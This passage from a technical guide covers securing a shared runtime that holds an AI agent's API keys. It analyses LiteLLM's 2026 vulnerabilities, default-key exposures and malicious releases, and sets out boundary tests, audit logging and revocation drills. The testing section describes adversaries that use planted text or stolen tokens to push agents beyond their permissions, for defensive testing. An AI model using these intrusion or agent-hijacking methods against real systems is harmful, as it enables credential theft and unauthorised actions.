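| Four independent runtimes with five keys each | 8% | 0.4 | About 1 in 6 million | 2.1 |

The 2% is an assumption, and a runtime's real risk could be lower or higher. One security team can probably protect a single service better than 20 teams protect 20 servers, but 20 keys in one place will attract more capable attackers. If only the average number of exposed credentials matters, the runtime is better whenever its risk is below that of a typical server.

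A shared runtime compares less well with separate servers when stolen keys do more damage together than they would separately. An attacker with the helpdesk, payments and mail keys can find customers who are waiting for refunds, look up what they paid, and write to them from the company's own address. If the loss grows with the square of the number of keys stolen, the runtime's risk of compromise would have to be below about 0.14% a year, a fourteenth of a single server's, to match the expected loss from 20 independent servers.

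But separate servers are rarely that independent. They often use the same libraries or cloud account, and a flaw in one of these can expose every server. Some costs, such as investigating a breach and notifying customers, also depend on the number of incidents, and the separate servers would have 0.4 breaches a year on average, 20 times as many as the runtime.

### LiteLLM, a gateway that holds many keys

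LiteLLM is an open-source gateway that companies put between their applications and the AI models they pay for. It stores the keys for all the model providers, applies budgets and rules, and can connect agents to tools through MCP. According to *Off Guard* (Shriki, 2026), a report from the security company Wiz, LiteLLM is present in about a third of the cloud environments Wiz has data on. Most of its keys are for models rather than services such as payments, but it has the structure of a shared runtime, and attackers targeted it repeatedly in 2026.

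The US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) added three LiteLLM flaws to its catalogue of vulnerabilities known to have been used by attackers during the year. It also added a flaw in a web component that LiteLLM relies on.

LiteLLM's MCP endpoint used separate login code from the rest of the gateway. It accepted LiteLLM keys, and it also accepted and passed on tokens meant for outside services such as GitHub. When a token failed the gateway's own check, the code treated it as possibly meant for an outside service and continued with an empty identity instead of refusing it. A made-up token could therefore open a session. This flaw, CVE-2026-59822, affected versions before 1.84.0 and has a severity score of 8.8 out of 10, according to Forkast.

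The design failed open because it treated a failed login as a possible success. The tools behind the gateway determined what an intruder could then do. One setting makes an MCP server available to every caller, including one with an empty identity. Shriki notes that LiteLLM's documentation recommended this setting for low-risk uses such as internal knowledge bases, but a company's knowledge base may contain much that outsiders shouldn't read.

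CISA added the flaw to its catalogue of exploited vulnerabilities on 2 September (eSecurity Planet, *CISA Adds 7 Exploited Flaws as Attackers Target AI Infrastructure*, 2026). The agency's notice, reproduced by viry.cz, cites "evidence of active exploitation". Wiz confirmed that hundreds of public instances were exploitable and saw attacks on its honeypots, decoy servers set up to attract intruders.

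LiteLLM's master key is the administrator's credential, and setting it turns on authentication. Before version 1.82.0, a gateway that started without a master key gave every request full administrator rights. Wiz scanned 3,074 public instances in February, and 294 (9.6%) accepted the example key printed in LiteLLM's setup guide. The operators of 191 of these had set no key, and the other 103 still used the example key, according to The Hacker News' *Nearly 1 in 10 Exposed LiteLLM Gateways Accepted the Example "sk-1234" Admin* (2026).

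There is no current figure. A scan in August found more than 85,000 instances, but Wiz believes most were honeypots or test systems. LiteLLM excludes attacks that depend on a setup mistake from its security policy, and in September its guide still showed the example key, with a comment that operators should replace it. The default was the design choice that failed. A gateway that refused to start without a long random key would have protected both groups.

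An administrator of a LiteLLM gateway could also make it forward requests to any address, including the cloud metadata address that returns the machine's own credentials. Wiz demonstrated this in tests, and The Hacker News found no report of its use against a real deployment. LiteLLM has not changed this behaviour because its design treats administrators as trusted.

Administrators could also submit Python code as a content filter, which the gateway ran with full privileges in its own container (CVE-2026-59821). LiteLLM rated this flaw 2.1 out of 10 because exploiting it requires a privileged account. That rating makes sense for a well-configured gateway, but anyone can act as an administrator on an instance that accepts the example key.

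**Other flaws.** Four more notices published by LiteLLM (2026) show different design failures:

| Notice | Flaw | Design choice that failed |
|---|---|---|
| March | Logs could contain callers' keys in plain text | A filter could return the whole request, and the gateway logged what it returned |
| April, CVE-2026-30623 | Any caller with a valid key could have the gateway run commands | The gateway started local MCP servers on the machine that held its keys |
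| April, CVE-2026-42208 | SQL injection in the check of callers' keys | The login code could reach the database behind the stored credentials |
| June, CVE-2026-48710 | Strangers could reach management pages in some set-ups | Access depended on a header that the caller supplied |

In April, LiteLLM also disclosed a login bypass that affected only installations that had enabled an optional type of signed login token. Like the MCP flaw, it was in a login path separate from the main one. A runtime with a single login path would have less code where such flaws could occur.

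Attackers used the LiteLLM SQL injection flaw within days of its disclosure, according to Paganini's *U.S. CISA adds a flaw in BerriAI LiteLLM to its Known Exploited* (2026). CISA added the flaw to its catalogue on 8 May and gave federal agencies until 11 May to act. In the catalogue entry, copied in thrunt's *BerriAI LiteLLM SQL Injection Vulnerability* (2026), CISA warns of access to the gateway and "the credentials it manages". In June, CISA confirmed attacks on another LiteLLM flaw, CVE-2026-42271, according to Help Net Security's *LiteLLM vulnerability under active attack, CISA warns (CVE-2026-42271)*. This command-injection flaw let attackers run commands on the machine hosting a service that stored many keys.

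### Two malicious releases

On 24 March, an attacker uploaded two malicious versions of LiteLLM to PyPI, the public index of Python packages. They were available for about 40 minutes and searched machines that installed them for cloud credentials, database passwords and other secrets. LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) tentatively traces the attack to Trivy, a security scanner used in its build process. An earlier attack had compromised Trivy, and LiteLLM believes the attacker then used stolen credentials to access its publishing account. The mistake was letting a third-party tool run where it could reach a credential for publishing releases.

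Companies that ran LiteLLM's official Docker image, a ready-made package of the gateway, were not affected because the image used fixed versions of its dependencies. Some separate tool servers were affected, including an MCP server belonging to FutureSearch that installed a malicious version as a dependency six minutes after its upload. A company with 20 such servers could have lost all 20 keys in the same hour, even without a shared runtime.

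*LiteLLM Supply-Chain Attack Exposed Credentials Across 2,500 Organizations* (Ofonagoro, 2026) reports an August estimate that the attack may have exposed credentials at more than 2,500 organisations. Trend Micro found that services holding many keys became "high-value collateral" in the wider campaign, which hadn't specifically targeted AI infrastructure.

After March, LiteLLM promised isolated build steps and short-lived publishing credentials (LiteLLM, *Security Townhall Updates*, 2026). The October attack used a different route, which *The attack chain behind the v1.107.0 LiteLLM release* (Jensen and Wang, 2026) describes step by step.

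On 27 May, a configuration file in one of LiteLLM's public repositories exposed the master key to an internal platform for coding agents. The team noticed quickly, removed the file and marked the exposed keys for revocation, but never revoked the master key. An attacker used it on 10 October, 136 days later.

The platform needed a GitHub token so that its agents could propose code changes. A service account with only that permission would have been enough, but the team had given the platform the GitHub organisation owner's token, which allowed full control of every repository. This was the same mistake as running the reconciliation job on Maria's token, but the owner's token allowed far more.

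The attacker used the owner's token to extract more secrets from build jobs, including the tokens of two maintainers. When the normal approval system blocked an attempt to redirect the release process, the attacker used the owner's token to turn the restriction off. Publishing a release normally required approval from an account tied to a physical device in the office, but that week the team had relaxed the rule so that any two engineers could trigger and approve a release, to publish fixes faster. The attacker triggered and approved a release with stolen tokens. The owner's token could have removed the rule anyway, as Jensen and Wang point out, so the unrestricted token was the more serious failure.

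LiteLLM's own pipeline then built, signed and published version 1.107.0 on 21 October, so its signature was valid. The release stayed on PyPI for about an hour and 45 minutes, and the Docker image was available for about an hour longer. The official image had protected its users in March, but this time its general tags, such as `latest`, pointed to the malicious version.

Cornelißen (2026) reports in *LiteLLM 1.107.0 war ein Credential-Stealer* that the malware also took model providers' keys from the gateway's own database. Singh (2026) found in *Compromised LiteLLM 1.107.0 on PyPI Installs a Credential Stealer and Backdoor* that the malware installed a backdoor and ran whenever any Python program started on the machine. LiteLLM says customers on its private enterprise release were unaffected.

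The blog index of LiteLLM (2026) lists a 23 November post announcing that the security firm Trail of Bits had helped harden the gateway and that fixes were "on the way".

### Exposure, attacks and losses

These incidents are easy to overstate, because reports often mix the number of systems at risk with the number that attackers reached.

| Event | Exposure | Observed attacks | Confirmed losses |
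|---|---|---|---|
| Example key or no key | 294 of 3,074 public instances in February | The scan didn't look for any | Unknown |
| CVE-2026-59822 | Hundreds of public instances | CISA listing, attacks on honeypots | Unknown |
| CVE-2026-42208 | Versions 1.81.16 to 1.83.6 | CISA listing, attacks within days | Unknown |
| March packages | Over 2,500 organisations, by one estimate | At least one documented infection | No reliable total |
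| October release | Anyone who installed it that day | Release published through the official pipeline | LiteLLM's own tokens and secrets; users' losses unknown |

A CISA listing is good evidence that someone has attacked a flaw, but it doesn't show how many companies lost keys. The October attacker certainly took LiteLLM's own credentials. According to *The plumbing is now the target (LiteLLM)* (Neely, 2026), it was still unknown at the end of that month how many users had installed the release.

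The case shows that attackers target gateways that hold many keys, and that ordinary mistakes can be enough to let them in. It doesn't provide a breach rate to replace the assumed 2%. LiteLLM is one very popular product, and researchers examined it more closely after March, which partly explains the number of flaws found.

### Controls and their costs

| Failure | Control | Main cost |
|---|---|---|
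| One break-in reaches every key | Separate runtimes by risk or customer | More services to run, and weaker rules across them |
| Submitted code runs beside the secrets | A vault process apart from policy and code execution | Another step in every call |
| An agent platform holds an owner's token | Short-lived, narrow tokens from service accounts | Setting up each permission, where the provider allows it |
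| A failed login or missing key gives access | Refusal by default, including at start-up | Some legitimate callers fail until someone configures them |
| The gateway can contact any address | An outbound host list enforced outside it | An update for every new API |
| A malicious release installs itself | Pinned dependencies | Slower security fixes |
| Nothing checks the runtime's decisions | A second check at the API | Two sets of rules to keep consistent |

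Splitting the 20 keys evenly among four runtimes leaves the average exposure at 0.4, but a break-in at one runtime exposes only five keys. The company could group APIs by risk, with payments in one runtime and low-risk reads in another. A business that runs agents for several customers could instead give each customer its own runtime. The runtimes need separate administrator keys and separate access to the vault, or one stolen credential will open all of them.

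The four runtimes would probably still run the same software, so one malicious release could compromise them all. Updating the payments runtime a few days after the others gives the company time to notice a malicious release before it reaches payments. The split also weakens rules that depend on several calls, such as the limit on mail after a charge look-up. Operations covered by the same rule should therefore stay in one runtime, unless the company is willing to run another shared service that tracks data labels across runtimes.

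**A separate vault process.** One process can authenticate callers and apply the policy, a second can run the agent's programs, and a third, like the credential-only proxy described earlier, can hold the keys and add them to requests. An intruder in the policy process could still request refunds but couldn't steal the payments key. Malware that searched the gateway's database, as the October release did, would find no keys there.

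The intruder could still issue refunds as long as they stayed in the policy process. To limit that, the vault process needs a rule of its own, such as a daily refund cap that the policy process can't change. The vault process should stay small, because every added feature increases the chance of a flaw in the process that holds the keys.

A token that expires after ten minutes gives a thief little time to use it. Okta's *LiteLLM supply chain attack* also recommends tokens that work only for a sender who can prove they hold a matching private key, so copying the token alone is not enough. Neither measure stops malware still running in the runtime, which can request new tokens or use the private key there. Many APIs offer only fixed keys. The company can restrict what such a key allows and should know how to replace it quickly.

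**Outbound host lists.** Both malicious releases sent the stolen secrets to look-alike domains unconnected with LiteLLM. A firewall outside the runtime that allowed connections only to the 20 APIs and a few known services would have blocked those transfers. The list has to be enforced outside the runtime because an intruder inside it could change the list. The firewall won't stop an intruder from sending data out through a permitted service, such as the mail API.

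Pinning dependencies means installing an exact, recorded version of each package instead of the newest one. *Hardening Your LLM Dependency Supply Chain*, published by Mozilla.ai, which makes a competing product, also recommends a private mirror that supplies only approved packages. A company that waited a week before approving ordinary updates would have avoided installing both malicious releases, because the maintainers and PyPI removed them within hours.

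But attackers used the SQL injection flaw within days of its disclosure, so delaying every update by a week would have been dangerous too. The company needs a faster route for security fixes, with someone to review each one. Jensen, Dholakia and Jaffer (2026) argue in *Introducing the LiteLLM Private Registry* that publishing a fix can itself show attackers how to exploit the flaw. Their answer is to distribute the most severe fixes privately before publishing them. Companies without access to the registry would get those fixes later.

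**A second check at the API.** This check still works when an intruder has full control of the runtime. If the payments company caps refunds on a key at $2,000 a day, and the support agent's company takes three days to notice the break-in, the agent's company loses at most $6,000 in refunds. The intruder could bypass the runtime's own $1,000 limit. If the payments company offers no cap, the separate payments server described earlier can apply one.

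### Attested execution

Remote attestation lets a machine give signed evidence of which software it is running. A verifier compares that evidence with what the company expects. *ACLE-MCP* (Ding, Luo and colleagues, 2026) applies this to individual tool calls, because an OAuth token shows that a caller may use a server but not that the server is still running the right software.

For a risky call, such as a refund, their system works as follows:

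1. The agent's host application states the limits of the call, such as the operation, the charge and the maximum amount.
2. A verifier checks fresh evidence of the software on the machine that will carry out the call.
3. An issuer combines this result with the OAuth permission into a short-lived lease, which is tied to the sender, the machine's software and the call's limits.
4. A gate in front of the tool checks the lease just before the tool runs, and refuses the call if anything doesn't match.

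The researchers compared five set-ups on six types of attack, ten times each. The attacks included using the wrong tool, reusing a permission and inserting an extra step. The times below are those within which 95% of normal requests finished.

| Set-up | Attacks blocked | Time |
|---|---|---|
| OAuth only | 0% | 12.20 ms |
| Software checked once, at connection | 0% | 17.30 ms |
| Rules on calls and their order, no software check | 83% | 11.06 ms |
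| Short-lived limited permission, no software check | 67% | 11.57 ms |
| Full ACLE-MCP | 100% | 15.34 ms |

The full system took 3.14 ms longer than OAuth alone, an increase of 25.7%. That delay is trivial compared with the time most web requests take, but it was measured in a local simulation with only 40 normal requests for each of those two set-ups. Two set-ups that did more checking than OAuth alone were slightly faster, so differences of about a millisecond are probably noise. The simulation also leaves out the overhead of real attestation hardware.

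Ordinary rules blocked five of the six attack types, so this test shows only a modest gain from attestation. In a second test, which shows its contribution more clearly, the full system blocked all 190 attacks. Without the software check, 30 got through, all involving compromised, substituted or mismatched software.

The evidence also has to be very recent. When the gate accepted evidence up to 50 milliseconds old, it caught every case in which the software changed between the check and the call. With a limit of 500 milliseconds it caught 60%, and with a limit of five seconds it caught none.

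Ding and colleagues assume that the gate, the verifier and the issuer are all sound and that no call can bypass the gate. An attacker who controls any of these three components can defeat the system. The system doesn't address prompt injection, so the dishonest refund would arrive with a valid lease. It also can't detect a call forwarded to an undeclared outside service that no network control covers.

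Attestation would also have done little against the LiteLLM attacks. The MCP login flaw was in the genuine software, which would have passed the check. The October release came from the official pipeline with a valid signature, so a company that approved new versions on that basis would have registered the malware as expected software. Attestation would help if an intruder replaced the approved software on a running machine. It may be worth the effort for the payments server, but the support agent's company should fix its defaults and narrow its keys first.

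### When the runtime is down

If the runtime is unavailable 0.1% of the time, no agent can use any API for about nine hours a year. If 20 separate servers each had the same amount of downtime at different times, at least one would be down for a total of about 174 hours a year, but they would almost never all be down at once.

Centralising makes a total stop more likely but can reduce interruptions to work that uses several APIs. A ticket that needs helpdesk, payments and mail would be stuck for about 26 hours a year with separate servers, because an outage on any of the three would stop it, compared with nine hours with the shared runtime.

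A gateway can also turn a small fault elsewhere into a full outage. LiteLLM (2026) reports that in April, when the gateway's database stopped responding, the gateway's attempt to reconnect typically froze the whole process for 30 to 120 seconds. The container management system treated the frozen copies of the gateway as failed and killed them, so a brief database problem stopped the gateway entirely.

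In September, one customer's model provider kept failing while Redis, the gateway's data store, was unreachable. The gateway recorded each failed attempt, and a bug in code meant to hide credentials roughly doubled the size of that record with every retry. One process grew to 61 GB of memory, and the operating system killed dozens of processes. Running more copies of the gateway didn't help because they all had the same bug and depended on the same data store.

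A useful fallback therefore needs its own database and should run an earlier version of the software, provided that version has the latest security fixes. Keeping such a copy ready and testing it costs money. A manual fallback may be enough for a company with a small support queue. Maria could log in to the payments company's website with her own account and issue urgent refunds herself, while the agent's other requests wait in a queue. Once the runtime is back, it should check each queued request again, since a ticket may have closed or an approval may have expired.

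The company shouldn't give agents the API keys directly during an outage, because their calls would then bypass the runtime's authorisation checks. For the same reason, the runtime refuses calls when its policy engine doesn't respond.

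## Testing the boundary and checking its logs

A runtime can block every forbidden call it receives and still fail as a boundary if anyone can reach the payments API without going through it. Testers should look for ways around the runtime before checking whether it allows and blocks the right calls.

### Routes around the runtime

The most likely way around the boundary is a copy of a key stored outside it. *The State of Secrets Sprawl 2026*, by GitGuardian, which sells tools for finding leaked secrets, reports 24,008 distinct secrets in MCP configuration files on public GitHub, of which 2,117 were valid. It attributes this partly to set-up guides that tell people to put keys in those files. About 28% of the incidents it counted began outside code repositories, in places such as Slack and Jira. It also reports 33,185 distinct secrets in data from 6,943 machines compromised in one attack.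 Most of those machines were build servers, so searching only laptops would miss many secrets.

A scanner can do part of the search. *Agent Audit* (2026) describes one that reads nine MCP configuration formats and flags exposed secrets and missing authentication. It won't find a key in someone's private notes. When the company moves payments into the runtime, it should therefore give a new key to the runtime alone and cancel the old one, so that any remaining copies stop working. Anything that then breaks was bypassing the runtime. Many companies seem to skip this step. When GitGuardian retested credentials that had been valid in 2022, more than 64% still worked in January 2026.

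The tester should also try to reach the tool servers directly. They send a harmless look-up to the payments server from a laptop, a build server and the agent's own sandbox, each time without the runtime's token. Every attempt should fail. A team's assurance that its server is internal isn't enough, as the exposed customer database in Zhou and colleagues' study showed.

The company's applications may already call APIs that nobody has added to the catalogue, which Dunkel calls the "shadow API problem". A DADL file can also record how much of an API it covers. The public file for GitHub, for instance, covers 205 of about 900 endpoints. Such a gap can become a security risk if an employee who needs a missing endpoint connects an agent to it with a personal key. Outbound network logs, software invoices and the list of applications connected to the company's SSO should reveal most missing APIs.

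The best way to find calls that bypass the runtime is to compare its log with records it doesn't write. Suppose the payments company lists 1,204 requests for one week and the runtime's log has 1,197. The other seven may be automatic retries, calls the runtime failed to record, or calls made from outside the runtime, so someone should trace all of them.

### A test for each caller and access level

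The next table applies the policy to six callers. "Ask" means that the runtime holds the call until a person approves it.

| Caller | Look up charge (read) | Add internal note (write) | Let an employee issue refunds (admin) | Delete customer record (dangerous) | Refund $40 (dangerous) |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Maria's agent, support role | Allow | Allow | Refuse | Refuse | Allow |
| Supervisor's agent | Allow | Allow | Refuse | Ask | Ask |
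| Administrator's agent | Allow | Allow | Ask | Ask | Ask |
| Reconciliation job | Allow | Refuse | Refuse | Refuse | Refuse |
| Employee who has left | Refuse | Refuse | Refuse | Refuse | Refuse |
| Caller without a token | Refuse | Refuse | Refuse | Refuse | Refuse |

Filling in the cells exposes a fault in the policy. Its exception for refunds names only the support role, so a supervisor's agent needs approval for a $40 refund that Maria's agent can issue without it. Before anyone runs the tests, the company should decide whether it wants this difference.

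A script using test accounts should send the calls, because a model might decline to make the forbidden ones. The tester should pair each forbidden call with a nearly identical one that should succeed. Otherwise, a misspelt operation name could produce an error that looks like a correct refusal. The tester should also confirm that nothing reached the payments test account.

The runtime fails the test if even one forbidden call gets through, whatever happens in the other 29 cells. Wrongly refused calls matter too, and Surapani and colleagues note that studies almost always leave them out.

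The script should repeat the calls through Code Mode if the runtime offers it. It should also call operations that the runtime hides from a caller. DunkelCloud says ToolMesh lists only the tools each caller may use, but an attacker could still guess a hidden tool's name.

Five more tests cover failures that the table misses:

| Test | Set-up | Expected result |
|---|---|---|
| Wrong audience | Send the runtime a valid, unexpired token issued for the helpdesk | A 401 error |
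| Expired grant | Use a ten-minute refund approval after 11 minutes | Refuse |
| Unlabelled operation | Delete one `access` line from a description file and misspell another | The runtime won't load either operation |
| Unreachable policy engine | Stop the policy server while calls are running | Refuse refunds at once, and reads when cached permissions expire |
| False context | Have the script claim to be working on a different ticket | The runtime uses the ticket recorded by the application |

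The policy-engine test should measure how long permissions keep working after they are withdrawn. *Sovereign Execution Broker* (2026) reports 1,000 tests in which a credential broker lost contact with the service that notifies it of withdrawn permissions. The broker refused every request, but only after its cached information had expired.

Surapani and colleagues list eight questions to answer before deployment, each with evidence such as a log excerpt or test result. They think most deployments would struggle with two of them. One is whether any permission depends on the model being truthful about its intent, which the false-context test partly covers. The other is whether two permitted tools could together disclose more than the task needs. The script tests this by looking up a charge and then trying to email an outside address, and the runtime should refuse the email.

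### Four adversaries to copy

In *Delegation Without Trust*, Dantuluri and Sundi (2026) tested whether an agent could exceed its permissions if an attacker controlled all of its model's output. Their four adversaries are easy to adapt into tests for the support agent.

| Adversary | What happens | Test for the support agent |
|---|---|---|
| Confused deputy | Planted text turns an agent's legitimate authority to the attacker's ends | Request a refund on a charge that the ticket's customer didn't pay |
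| Token theft | The attacker copies a credential and uses it elsewhere | Send the agent's token from another machine |
| Privilege escalation | Planted text makes an agent use permissions its task doesn't need | Call the operation that lets an employee issue refunds |
| Compromised sub-agent | A second agent has more authority than its job requires | Give a second agent one charge to look up, then have it try everything else |

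They first built a default runtime modelled on common practice. It gave the first agent one broad credential, passed that credential unchanged to other agents and tools, and let the agent decide what to do through its own reasoning. All four adversaries succeeded. They then added a broker between the agents and the tools, which blocked all four.

Each time one agent hands work to another, the broker issues a new short-lived token. The token covers only the sub-task and works only for the receiving agent's machine identity. Before each tool call, the broker checks the token's signature, its limits, who is presenting it and whether anyone has revoked it.

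Dantuluri and Sundi wrote the default runtime without any of the controls they were testing for, so it was bound to fail. Their attacks on the broker are more informative. They tried 11, including removing a token's limits and using a token derived from a revoked one, and none worked. The broker also rejected all 200,000 random or altered tokens, but this adds little evidence because guessing a valid signature is practically impossible. As they expected, a stolen token did work for an attacker who could also present the victim's machine identity. If the support agent's token isn't tied to a machine identity, the stolen token will work in the token-theft test, and the company should record this as a known gap.

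They also measured how far a compromised sub-agent could reach in 2,000 simulated scenarios with 8,100 possible actions. It could reach all 8,100 under the default runtime and an average of 1.5 under the broker. The 1.5 reflects how small the simulated tasks were. The more important result is that the sub-agent's reach under the broker doesn't grow when a company adds APIs. The support agent's company can measure reach too, by counting how many operations the second agent can call.

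The tests didn't use a live model, the code isn't public, and Dantuluri and Sundi work for a company that sells a related product. A company that passes all four tests might still be unable to stop the dishonest refund, because the refund could fall within the agent's task.

The study's comparison of agent frameworks mixes different kinds of evidence:

| System | How they examined it | Adversaries stopped by default |
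|---|---|---|
| LangGraph 1.2.10 | Ran it, with a script in place of the model | None |
| CrewAI 1.15.13 | Read its code | None |
| AutoGen 0.7.5 | Read its code | None |
| MCP authorisation rules, July 2026 | Read the specification | Token theft, in part |

Only the LangGraph result comes from running a framework. None of the three frameworks is presented as an authorisation system, and developers can add their own checks. The MCP result is the least certain because two of the study's tables contradict each other. One lists partial support for key rotation and revocation but none for audit records, while the other lists partial support for audit records but none for key rotation and revocation.

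### What to record about each call

The runtime should write a record for every decision, including refusals. These are the fields the support agent's company would need:

| Field | Purpose |
|---|---|
| Time and request ID | Match the call to the provider's log and to any retries |
| Task | Connect the call to the ticket that the application opened |
| User and agent | Distinguish Maria from the software acting for her |
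| Operation and access level | Preserve the label in force at the time |
| Arguments | Show the charge and amount, without secrets or needless personal data |
| Sources | List the outside text in the model's input |
| Decision and rule | Explain why the call went through or failed |
| Policy version | Let a reviewer repeat the decision under the same rules |
| Credential identifier | Name the key, but never include its value |
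| Credential sent | Show whether the key left the runtime |
| Result | Give the API's answer, if there was one |

Suppose the customer behind ticket 9160 asks for a refund on `ch_4821`, which customer 2207 paid. The runtime refuses the call and writes this record:

```json
{
  "time": "2026-12-04T10:42:07Z",
  "request_id": "req_70c1",
  "task": "ticket-9160",
  "user": "maria@company.example",
  "agent": "support-agent",
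  "operation": "payments.issue_refund",
  "access_level": "dangerous",
  "arguments": { "charge_id": "ch_4821", "amount": 4000, "currency": "USD" },
  "sources": ["ticket-9160: untrusted"],
  "decision": "refuse",
  "rule": "ticket-customer-must-be-payer",
  "policy_version": "2026-12-01.3",
  "credential_id": "vault/payments-key",
  "credential_sent": false,
  "result": null
}
```

Default values can make an incomplete record look complete. In the table definition in Cisco's *Audit store* for its DefenseClaw product, the actor defaults to `defenseclaw` when an event doesn't name one. That makes sense for events the product starts itself, but a tool call without a known user should produce an obvious error.

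Removing secrets by field name can also leave some in the logs. According to Zscaler's *Tool-Call Audit Logging*, its MCP server hides any argument whose name contains a word such as `password`, `token` or `key`, so a key pasted into the body of an email would stay in the log. ToolMesh's debug log includes full web addresses, so it can expose keys that an API requires in the address. The tester can check for leaks by storing a unique dummy key, making both successful and failed calls with it, and searching every log for its value.

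The company also has to decide where to store the records and how long to keep them. Solace's *Managing Audit and Compliance* says that its agent runtime has no audit database of its own and leaves storage and retention to the operator. Surapani and colleagues recommend logs that only accept additions, with each record containing a hash (a short digital fingerprint) of the one before, so that later changes are detectable. An intruder who controls the runtime could rewrite the records and recompute all the hashes, so a separate system should hold a copy that the runtime can't change.

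### What a log can't establish

The record of a successful refund shows that Maria was logged in, that her agent requested the refund and that the policy allowed it. It doesn't show that Maria wanted the refund, because she may only have told the agent to deal with her tickets.

Surapani and colleagues distinguish proving that someone's key signed an approval from proving that the person intended the resulting action. Digital signatures can reliably prove the signing, but more cryptography can't prove intent, because the model's reasoning turns the person's request into the final call. A supervisor's approval of the exact charge and amount is much better evidence of intent, though the supervisor may have approved it without reading it.

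The `sources` field has a similar limit. It shows that the model had read ticket 9160 before it requested the refund, but not that the ticket caused the request. The runtime also can't record calls that bypass it, and the provider's log may not show that an agent made them. *Agent Authenticator* (2026) points out that outside services often can't distinguish an agent's actions from those of the person it works for.

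Surapani and colleagues cite a 2026 industry survey in which only 28% of organisations could connect an agent's action to a person across all their systems.

### A revocation drill

Revocation withdraws a permission before it would have expired. The company should practise it, because an administrator's screen may show an account as disabled while its agents are still making calls. A drill could run as follows:

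1. A script looks up a test charge once a second as Maria's agent. A second agent, working for the first, does the same.
2. The tester leaves one test refund waiting for approval.
3. An administrator disables Maria's test account and notes the time.
4. Both scripts keep running until the runtime refuses them.
5. A supervisor approves the waiting refund, which the runtime should now refuse.
6. An administrator replaces the payments test key, and the tester tries the old one directly at the payments API.
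7. Someone who didn't prepare the drill lists everything Maria's agents did that day.

| Time to measure | Likely cause if it's long |
|---|---|
| Until the first agent's last accepted call | Cached permissions or long-lived tokens |
| Until the second agent's last accepted call | Exchanged tokens that outlive the original |
| Until the runtime cancels or refuses the waiting refund | No second check when the approval arrives |
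| From replacing the key until the old one fails | Nobody cancelled it at the provider |
| Until the list of calls is complete | Split or incomplete logs |

Step 6 matters because announcing a revocation isn't the same as carrying it out, as LiteLLM's overlooked master key showed.

*VERA* (2026) calculates how many calls could still go through after a revocation by multiplying the call rate by the sum of the token's lifetime and the time the revocation takes to spread. If an agent makes two calls a second with five-minute tokens, and the revocation takes five seconds to spread, the agent could make 2 × (300 + 5) = 610 more calls.

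Checking for revocations more often reduces this number. The broker in *Sovereign Execution Broker* checked for updates every five seconds and kept each result for five seconds. It took 2.6 seconds on average to start refusing all requests, and 5.2 seconds at most. At two calls a second, an agent could make about ten more calls in the slowest case. The company could also check every token online before each call, which *Crypto-bound identity-verified capability tokens for coordinating distributed AI agents* (2026) describes as worth the extra delay in most cases. For the support agent, the delay is worthwhile at least for refunds.

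The drill should also include one request in progress at the moment of revocation, to confirm that the log records its outcome.

### Re-checking labels

A label can become wrong after its initial review if the provider changes its API. DADL has a `last_reviewed` date, but it covers a whole API's entry, so the date can be recent even if nobody has looked at one of the operations for a year. The company should record a review date for each label.

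Every three months, a reviewer could check the operations that changed, the ones agents call most and a random sample of the rest. If the provider's records show that a customer record changed during a call labelled `read`, the label is probably wrong. The company can also test its reviewers by putting ten wrong labels in a copy of the catalogue. If they find only six, they are probably missing real mistakes too.

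### Warning signs

Some signs of a failing boundary appear in ordinary use, between formal tests:

| Sign | What may be wrong |
|---|---|
| The provider's log has calls that the runtime's log lacks | Someone has another key, or logging has failed |
| The payments key is still in use while the runtime is off | A copy exists elsewhere |
| The log has no refusals for weeks | The checks may be off, or the policy may allow too much |
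| Nearly all calls have the same user | Several people or agents share one login |
| Copies of the runtime report different policy versions | An update reached only some of them |
| Approvers accept every request within seconds | They have stopped reading |
| The list of exceptions keeps growing | The roles or labels don't fit the work |

ToolMesh's simplest set-up can produce the shared-login sign. It uses a single API key, whose holder is by default a user called `owner` with the administrator role. If a whole team uses that key, the log attributes every call to `owner`, and every agent has the owner's permissions.

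In development mode, ToolMesh logs relaxed security settings at start-up as routine information, not warnings, so a production system left in that mode could run without authorisation checks and without a warning. Making a daily test call that the runtime should refuse, and sending an alert if it succeeds, would catch this sooner than waiting for someone to read the log.
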